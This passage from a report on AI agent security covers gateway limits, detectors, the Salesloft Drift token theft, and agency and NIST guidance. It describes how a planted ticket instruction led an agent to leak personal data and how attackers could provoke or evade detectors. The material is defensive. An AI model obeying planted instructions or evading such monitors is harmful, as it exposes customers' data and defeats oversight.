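An attacker can steal data too quickly for a person to intervene, and sometimes too quickly for revocation to work. At 100 records a second, an attacker whose token works for ten more minutes can take 60,000 records. The gateway should therefore refuse the calls itself rather than wait for the token to expire. A limit of one record a second would reduce the theft to 600 records and hardly affect the support agent, whose lookups are more than a minute apart on average.

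### The Salesloft Drift theft

A theft in August 2025 shows what such rules could have used. Salesloft's Drift product powers AI chatbots on corporate websites and connects to customers' Salesforce records. Infosecurity Magazine's *Salesloft* reports that attackers had access to Salesloft's GitHub account between March and June. They later entered Drift's cloud systems and stole the OAuth tokens for customers' connections. The attackers used the chatbot's credentials without hijacking a model.

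The theft from Salesforce ran from 8 August to at least 18 August, according to Google's account of the attack, *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* (Larsen, Lin and colleagues, 2025). Google knew of over 700 potentially affected organisations, The Hacker News (2025) reported. One was Cloudflare, an internet infrastructure company, whose timeline appears in Decipher's *Cloudflare Details Salesloft Drift Breach* (2025) and on the news site Salesforce Ben.

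| Date in August 2025 | What happened at Cloudflare | What a rule could have used |
|---|---|---|
| 9 | Attackers tried to validate a Cloudflare token for Salesforce | A token used from an unfamiliar address |
| 12 | They entered with Drift's stolen credential | Drift's account connecting from outside Drift |
| 16 | They checked how much data there was | A chatbot measuring whole tables |
| 17 | A bulk job copied the text of support cases in just over three minutes | A chatbot starting a bulk export |
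| 20 | Salesloft revoked all Drift connections to Salesforce | Too late |
| 23 | Salesforce and Salesloft notified Cloudflare | Too late |

The simplest rule would have accepted Drift's token only from Drift's own servers. Google listed 20 addresses that the attackers used, and 18 were exit points of Tor, a network that hides where a connection comes from and that a chatbot vendor has no obvious reason to use. Another address belonged to Amazon's cloud, where Drift ran, so the rule would have needed to list Drift's exact addresses rather than allow all of Amazon's cloud. Even that might not have stopped attackers who were already inside Drift's systems, because they could have sent their queries from there.

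A rule about the order of calls would have helped against that. Larsen and colleagues found that the attackers first counted the rows in four kinds of record, including accounts, users and support cases, and then requested up to 10,000 cases at once. A chatbot that handles one visitor at a time should rarely need to do either. Stopping the connection after the first measurement would have given Cloudflare a day to investigate before the export.

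A volume rule would have worked only if it could block the bulk job before it ran or stop it partway. An hourly check would most likely have found the job already finished. Uber's system also collects its records once an hour, which is often enough for an investigation but too slow to stop a three-minute theft. Any of these rules would have had to run at Salesforce, because the queries went straight there and not through the customers' own gateways.

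These judgements are based on the published timeline and benefit from hindsight, but the evidence was available. The logs remained after the attackers deleted their query jobs.

The Drift tokens were revoked three days after Cloudflare lost its data. The first notice to customers, on 20 August, contained instructions to reconnect Drift but no mention of stolen tokens, as Krebs on Security (2025) reported. Google issued a public warning on 26 August, and two days later advised customers to treat every token connected to Drift as potentially compromised, including those for services other than Salesforce.

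The number of records stolen is also a poor measure of loss, because one support case containing a cloud access key could be worth more to an attacker than thousands of ordinary cases. The attackers in this theft searched the stolen data for passwords and cloud access keys, and Cloudflare warned that any key a customer had pasted into a support case should be considered compromised.

### Choosing a response

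A company can block an unusual transfer without shutting down the agent. A milder response costs less when the detector is wrong, so the company can use it on weaker evidence. The costs below are invented, and each break-even probability assumes that the response prevents a $50,000 loss.

| Response | What the agent can still do | Cost if wrong | Break-even probability |
|---|---|---|---|
| Slow it to one record a second | Everything, but more slowly | $5 | 0.01% |
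| Hold the call for a person | Other calls | $20 | 0.04% |
| Refuse the call | Other calls | $50 | 0.1% |
| Revoke its database token | Work that needs no customer records | $1,000 | 2% |
| Isolate it from every system | Nothing | $10,000 | 17% |

An alert alone disrupts legitimate work even less, but the transfer continues until someone acts. At 100 records a second, an agent will have transferred 30,000 records by the time an analyst responds five minutes later. Slowing the agent gives the analyst more time to respond to the alert. Refusing one call may not be enough, since a hijacked agent can try another route. The company could therefore refuse the first suspicious call and revoke the token only if more evidence appears.

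*Intrusion-Detection Policies for IT Security Breaches* reaches a similar view from the economics of detection. Acting on every signal is costly when intruders are rare, but ignoring signals makes the detector useless. The paper proposes waiting-time policies for deciding how to respond. For an agent, waiting is acceptable only if something limits how much data can leave in the meantime.

An agent needs a clear response when a transfer is blocked or a policy refuses its request, or it might keep retrying and set off more alarms. For unapproved tools, *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2025) recommends that the gateway return an explicit "tool unavailable" message, with none of the tool's output, and notify the user.

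### Blocks that an attacker provokes

An attacker can cause wrong blocks on purpose, for example with malicious tickets that trigger an automatic cut-off like AgentCap's. The break-even formula doesn't account for this because it assumes wrong blocks are accidental. If each isolation cost $10,000 (an invented figure), five successful attempts would cost the company $50,000, as much as the theft it was trying to prevent.

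Keeping a separate score for each ticket reduces this risk. *Agent Control Protocol* (2026) tested a system that at first kept one score for the whole agent. After eleven harmless requests in one context, the system raised the risk score of a legitimate request in another context from 50 to 70 and denied it instead of sending it for review. With separate scores for each context, the system sent the legitimate request to review as intended. Eleven repeated requests within a single context still led to a denial.

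An attacker could get around separate ticket scores by opening 50 tickets and taking one stranger's record through each. The company also needs a total across tickets, but that total should trigger a slower rate or an alert, not isolation. Blocking the sender of a suspicious ticket is also better than blocking the agent that read it.

### When the detector itself fails

The company has to decide in advance what the gateway does if the detector stops responding. If the gateway fails open, it lets calls through unchecked, and an attacker who can overload the detector can steal data freely. If it fails closed, it refuses the calls, and the same attacker can stop all the company's agents.

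Whether to fail open or closed can differ by tool. Looking up an order's delivery status with a token for one ticket could fail open, because little can go wrong. Bulk exports and changes to payment details should fail closed, since they can usually wait an hour. Simple limits, such as five lookups per ticket, can run in the gateway, so they keep working without the detector.

Overload is more common than complete failure, and Canale compared three ways to handle it. Queueing every event caused no attacks to be missed but delayed detection by hours or days, too late to block anything. Dropping events kept the delay to about a minute but missed attacks. The third method left out performance-monitoring logs, which made up 14% of events and did not measurably improve detection. This kept the detection rate up, but the delay still grew when the remaining traffic exceeded capacity.

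## What do governments and standards bodies ask organisations to do?

During 2026, security agencies and standards bodies published several documents on how organisations should choose and pay for an AI agent's controls, and answer for the result when those controls fail. Nearly all of these documents are advisory. Binding duties come mostly from older laws, which have no special rules for agents but cover the data and services that agents use.

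### Six agencies on adopting agents

The broadest document is the Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026). The directorate wrote it with five agencies from Canada, New Zealand, the United Kingdom and the United States, including the NSA and CISA. CISA (2026) announced it on 1 May. It is general guidance with no deadlines or penalties and, according to its disclaimer, is not legal advice.

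The agencies tell organisations to use agents only for "low-risk and non-sensitive tasks". Taken literally, that rules out the support agent, which opens customer records all day. But the same document describes human approval for high-impact actions, which would be unnecessary if agents never took any. It also recommends starting with little access and adding more as evaluations justify it. The support company could start with delivery questions and give the agent access to order statuses but not phone numbers or home addresses. The agencies also suggest asking whether a repetitive task needs an agent, and a tracking link in the dispatch email might prevent many of the delivery questions.

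One of the document's hypothetical scenarios closely resembles the support company's situation. An agent sorts support tickets and fetches account information. The organisation adds a scheduling component from another vendor and gives it broad access without a thorough review. An attacker takes over the component. Because the agent reuses old permission decisions instead of checking each request, the attacker can run account-management functions, then move on to the agents that handle billing and refunds.

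The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners want each agent to have its own cryptographic keys and an entry in a trusted registry. Services should refuse any agent that isn't in the registry, and staff should regularly compare the registry with the agents actually running. The agencies also recommend mutual TLS for every call between agents and services, so that a caller can't later deny having made a call (non-repudiation). Mutual TLS alone can't ensure this, because it proves the caller's identity to the server during the connection but leaves no signed request that an outsider could check afterwards.

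The agencies list network egress among the actions that may need a person's approval, and every reply the support agent sends is egress. Staff who had to review all 400 replies a day would be likely to approve some carelessly. The agencies let the system's designers or operators, but not the agent, decide when approval is necessary, so the company could review only unusual replies.

The joint guidance covers systems with "one or more agents", including those with a single agent, although the law firm Reed Smith describes it as focused on systems of several agents working together. In July the Australian Signals Directorate (2026) published shorter advice that refers to the joint guidance and mentions live monitoring, logs and a way to halt an agent.

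### The NSA's recommendations for MCP

After criticising MCP, the NSA made recommendations for organisations that still use it. It wrote the paper for national security systems, the Department of War and defence contractors, but allows wider sharing. The paper is advisory, even for its intended readers.

Many popular MCP servers no longer have active maintainers, so the NSA recommends choosing supported projects, putting their code through the organisation's strictest review and listing the approved ones in an internal registry. It also advises organisations to group tools by the sensitivity of their data, which would keep the support company's customer lookup apart from a public weather service. Each tool should run in a sandbox that blocks access to files and networks it doesn't need. Developers should treat a tool's output as untrusted input to the next step, even if they have vetted the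 tool.

Organisations should also record the version and patch history of every MCP agent and tool. The paper gives the example of a flaw in MCP Inspector, a program for testing servers, that let attackers run their own code until version 0.14.1 fixed it. A company with an up-to-date inventory can find its old copies quickly, without having to ask every developer.

The NSA prefers a local MCP server for private data, to reduce leaks. This could backfire if the server runs on an employee's laptop, where network monitoring would miss a stdio server's messages. Running the server on the company's own machines behind a gateway would keep the data in-house and still let the company monitor the calls. But the agency warns that security proxies built for MCP are still immature, which is a reason to keep other controls behind the gateway.

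### NIST's project on agent identity

NIST's concept paper dates from 5 February 2026 and was open for public comment until 2 April. It is a draft project proposal with questions for public comment, so it imposes no requirements. Booth and colleagues plan to build an example system from commercial products in a NIST laboratory and publish a practice guide on how they did it. The result would be implementation guidance, not mandatory controls, as Attribit, a website on agent identity, points out.

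Besides OAuth and SPIFFE, the candidate standards include SCIM (System for Cross-domain Identity Management), which is used to create, update and remove accounts across systems. SCIM could help a company remove an agent's accounts from many services at once, but it doesn't authenticate anyone. The possible use cases are office work, security analysis and software development. Customer support isn't included, although most of the identity work would apply there too.

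NIST has also begun a series of blog posts. The first, in August, drew on comments about the concept paper. *Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems* (Booth, 2026) followed on 27 October with principles, also advisory, for designing identity systems.

NIST's planned control overlays may eventually have more effect. An overlay adapts controls from NIST's general security catalogue, SP 800-53, to one type of system. Attribit reports that the planned set will address both single agents and groups of agents, and that NIST had published none for agents as of March 2026. US federal agencies already have to use the catalogue, so an overlay would fit into their existing process. A private company could ignore it unless a contract required it.

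Industry groups publish their own advice, such as the Coalition for Secure AI's *Agentic Identity and Access Management* (2026), which reached version 1.0 in March.

### Where the law already applies

An agent has no legal personality, so the organisation that runs it keeps its existing duties. Three European Union laws show how those duties apply to the use of agents.

| Law | Whom it binds | What it means for an agent |
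|---|---|---|
| General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) | Organisations that handle personal data in the EU, or offer goods or services to people there | Security must suit the risk; suppliers that process data need a contract; the organisation must report most breaches to a regulator within 72 hours |
| NIS2 Directive, through national laws | Mostly medium and large organisations in sectors such as energy, transport and health | Risk management must cover access, assets and suppliers; a significant incident needs an early warning within 24 hours |
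| Digital Operational Resilience Act (DORA) | Banks, insurers and other financial firms | Firms must limit access, control software changes, register technology suppliers and report major incidents |

Suppose Pat lives in the EU. When the support agent emailed Pat's phone number and address to a stranger, the company suffered a personal data breach under the GDPR. It had 72 hours to report the breach after becoming aware of it. The company still had this duty even though a planted instruction caused the breach, and its security may still have been inadequate. If the risk to Pat was high, the company also had to tell Pat.

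The support company isn't a financial firm, but DORA could still affect it through a customer. A bank that outsourced its support to the company would have to write security terms into the contract and list the contract in its register. DORA's rules on software changes would also give the bank a reason to ask what happens when the agent's model changes.

The United States has no general equivalent of the GDPR. Organisations' duties there come from state laws and sector rules, such as the HIPAA Security Rule for health records.

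Advice can also gain legal weight indirectly. A customer can write the six agencies' recommendations into a contract. The GDPR requires organisations to take account of the state of the art in security, and a regulator could use published guidance as evidence of what the state of the art was at the time. A company that gave an agent unrestricted access after agencies from five countries had warned against doing so might struggle to show that its security was appropriate.

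### One agent from registration to retirement

The documents agree on enough to outline a life cycle for the support agent. It starts with an entry in the company's register:

```text
Agent         support-agent
Identity      spiffe://prod.example.com/ns/support/sa/support-agent
Owner         head of customer support
Deputy        support operations manager
Purpose       answer customers' tickets
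Tools         open, read and close ticket; get_customer; send_email
Data          only the record of the customer who wrote in
Never         change payment details; export records
Model         <provider and version>
Next review   2027-03-05, or before any change of model, tools or data
Can stop it   security engineer on call
```

The six agencies want organisations to define who owns the risk, but they don't assign the jobs. The last column below therefore shows one workable arrangement.

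| Step | What happens to the support agent | Who decides |
|---|---|---|
| Registration | An engineer records it, and the gateway refuses agents without an entry | Security team |
| Ownership | The head of support accepts the risk in writing | Chief operating officer |
| Tools and data | It gets the listed tools and one customer's record per ticket | Head of support proposes; security and privacy staff approve |
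| Launch | It answers delivery questions first, then other tickets | Head of support, with the security team's agreement |
| Change | Engineers replay old tickets and planted attacks | Head of support and security team |
| Incident | The agent stops and staff take over its tickets | Security engineer on call stops it; head of support and security team restart it |
| Retirement | Staff cancel its credentials and mark the entry as retired | Head of support decides; security team confirms |

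The owner should be the head of support rather than the developer who built the agent. A developer can fix a fault but usually has no authority to accept a risk to customers or to spend money on reducing it. The security team also needs a veto, because the head of support gains from every extra ticket the agent answers.

Changes are the step the company is most likely to miss, because a model provider or the operator of a remote MCP server can change its service without the company's approval. The company should use a fixed model version where the provider offers one, and have the gateway withhold any tool whose description has changed. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners also recommend being able to return to an earlier version that behaved well. For a hosted model, that works only until the provider retires the old version. The company might then fall back on an agent that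 answers only delivery questions.

The incident plan has to cover how staff will do the agent's work while it is stopped, as well as how they will respond to the attack. If staff need five minutes per ticket, 400 tickets take about 33 hours, which is more than four people can do in a working day. If not enough people are available, managers will be under pressure to leave a suspicious agent running. The engineer on call should be able to stop the agent at night without finding its owner first. The plan also needs to name who preserves the logs, who contacts customers and who decides whether to notify a regulator. New Business reprints advice from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre that response plans should cover an agent's failure, its misuse and loss of control over it.

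When a company retires an agent, it should keep the agent's register entry, because a customer may complain about a leak months later. Regularly comparing the register with running agents will then also reveal any that are still making calls after being marked as retired, which need immediate attention. The same comparison can identify registered agents that haven't made a call for three months and are probably ready to retire.

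### Do agents need new identity standards?

NIST argues that companies should build on existing identity standards, though it expects those standards to evolve. Infosys' *Enterprise AI identity and access architecture* objects that company identity systems assume human users, whereas an agent may run for minutes and act for several people in one task. But the methods it examines, including workload attestation, short-lived credentials and token exchange, already exist.

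The OpenID Foundation (2026), responding to a NIST request for information, said the gap was in deployment. Users and agents expect fine-grained decisions from identity systems that are still maturing in practice. On that view, a company's first problem is that it hasn't installed or finished configuring what is available.

A commenter from the company Hushmesh made a deeper objection under NIST's August post. When one organisation accepts another's agent, it also relies on the other's administrators, key storage and policy systems, most of which the identity protocol doesn't show. Each further organisation in a chain adds more hidden dependencies. Hushmesh wants a new design that links agents, people and organisations cryptographically, so that others can verify these dependencies. It has worked on such a design for years, so it has an interest in seeing one adopted.

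Ordinary software has this problem too, and companies manage it with contracts and audits. It becomes more serious if agents start choosing partners while they run, because nobody can negotiate a contract while an agent is handling a ticket. The support agent mostly works inside one company, where existing standards can identify it well enough.

Standards bodies are mostly extending their existing work. Flanagan (2026), in *What Exactly Are We Identifying When We Identify an AI Agent?*, reports that agent identity came up repeatedly at the IETF's 127th meeting, in the OAuth and WIMSE groups and in a session on tracing delegation. Flanagan found much of the discussion familiar because these communities have worked on authentication, delegation and accountability for decades.

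### Should companies wait?

None of the agencies asks companies to stop using agents. The NSA comes closest, saying that the gaps in MCP must be closed before anyone can use it confidently in security-critical settings. The joint guidance puts reversibility and containment ahead of efficiency until standards and testing methods mature. The UK advice is to start small, and the Australian Signals Directorate writes in its July text of balancing innovation with security.

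One reason to wait is that some harm is permanent, such as Pat's address reaching a stranger's inbox. Another is that the controls are still changing, so a company that builds on them now may have to rebuild.

However, an employee can set up an agent in minutes, so a company that forbids agents may end up with unregistered ones. The agencies also don't define when the controls will be mature enough, so a company that decided to wait wouldn't know when to stop.

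Delaying particular actions makes more sense than delaying whole agents. The support agent can look up a parcel's status now, since a mistake does little harm, and it can draft unusual replies for staff. It should not send personal data to new addresses until the company has tested the agent's limits with planted attacks, because sending the data can't be undone.

### Why NIST left out other people's agents

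Booth and colleagues exclude external agents that come from untrusted sources because a company can better see and control its own agents and the systems they use. They leave public-facing and individual agents for possible later phases. Attacks from outside remain in scope, and they ask how to prevent prompt injection and limit the damage after it happens.

Suppose Dana's personal AI assistant logs in to the support company's website with Dana's password. The company didn't issue the assistant's identity, can't inspect its software and may not notice that it isn't Dana. NIST says that work on authenticators for such agents, tied to their users' identities, is at an early stage. It is reasonable to start with company agents, because a laboratory can build a working example with products already on sale.

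The omission still matters to any business with a website. In comments to NIST, industry coalitions asked for standards that bind an agent to the person who authorised it. The Center for Cybersecurity Policy, which published the comments, notes that current bot detection is mainly designed to block automation and can't confirm that a customer sent the bot. Without that confirmation, a company may turn away Dana's assistant or admit an impostor.

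Identifying agents also puts privacy at risk. Flanagan asks what it means for the people behind the agents. If Dana's assistant used the same identifier at a shop, a clinic and a bank, the three could combine their records about Dana. A standard for outside agents would have to let an agent prove that Dana gave permission without creating a permanent number that could be used to track Dana.

The US government has no unified system across its agencies for establishing an AI agent's identity, according to the US intelligence official Doug Cossa, as reported in PYMNTS's *US Intelligence Chief Calls for Digital IDs for AI Agents* (2026).

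### What organisations have done, and whether it helps

Many surveys on agent security come from companies that sell it. SailPoint, which sells identity software, sponsored *AI Agents: The New Attack Surface* (2025), a Dimensional Research survey of 353 IT professionals. It found that 82% of their organisations used agents but only 44% had policies for securing them. The survey predates the joint guidance by a year, so it doesn't measure the guidance's effect. Organisations that have a policy also may not enforce it.

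IBM's *Cost of a Data Breach Report 2025*, researched by the Ponemon Institute, covered 600 organisations that had suffered breaches. Of these, 13% reported a breach of an AI model or application, and 97% of that group lacked proper access controls for AI. The 97% figure does not show that access controls work, because it has no comparison group. If 95% of organisations without an AI breach also lacked the controls, having them would have made little difference. The report also covers AI in general, not just agents.

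No published study appears to show that organisations following the 2026 guidance have fewer incidents. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners write that weak evaluation methods can make reliable validation of agent security "nearly impossible". Some technical controls, such as checking each tool call against fixed rules, have stopped most attacks in experiments. The case for registers and named owners rests on reasoning and on experience with older systems.

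Counting incidents could make good practice look harmful, because a company with better logs discovers more of its own leaks. A fairer test would send the same harmless planted instructions to every agent and count how often marked test data got out. A company with 100 agents could apply the full life cycle to 50 chosen at random, test all 100 after three months, and then apply the life cycle to the other 50.
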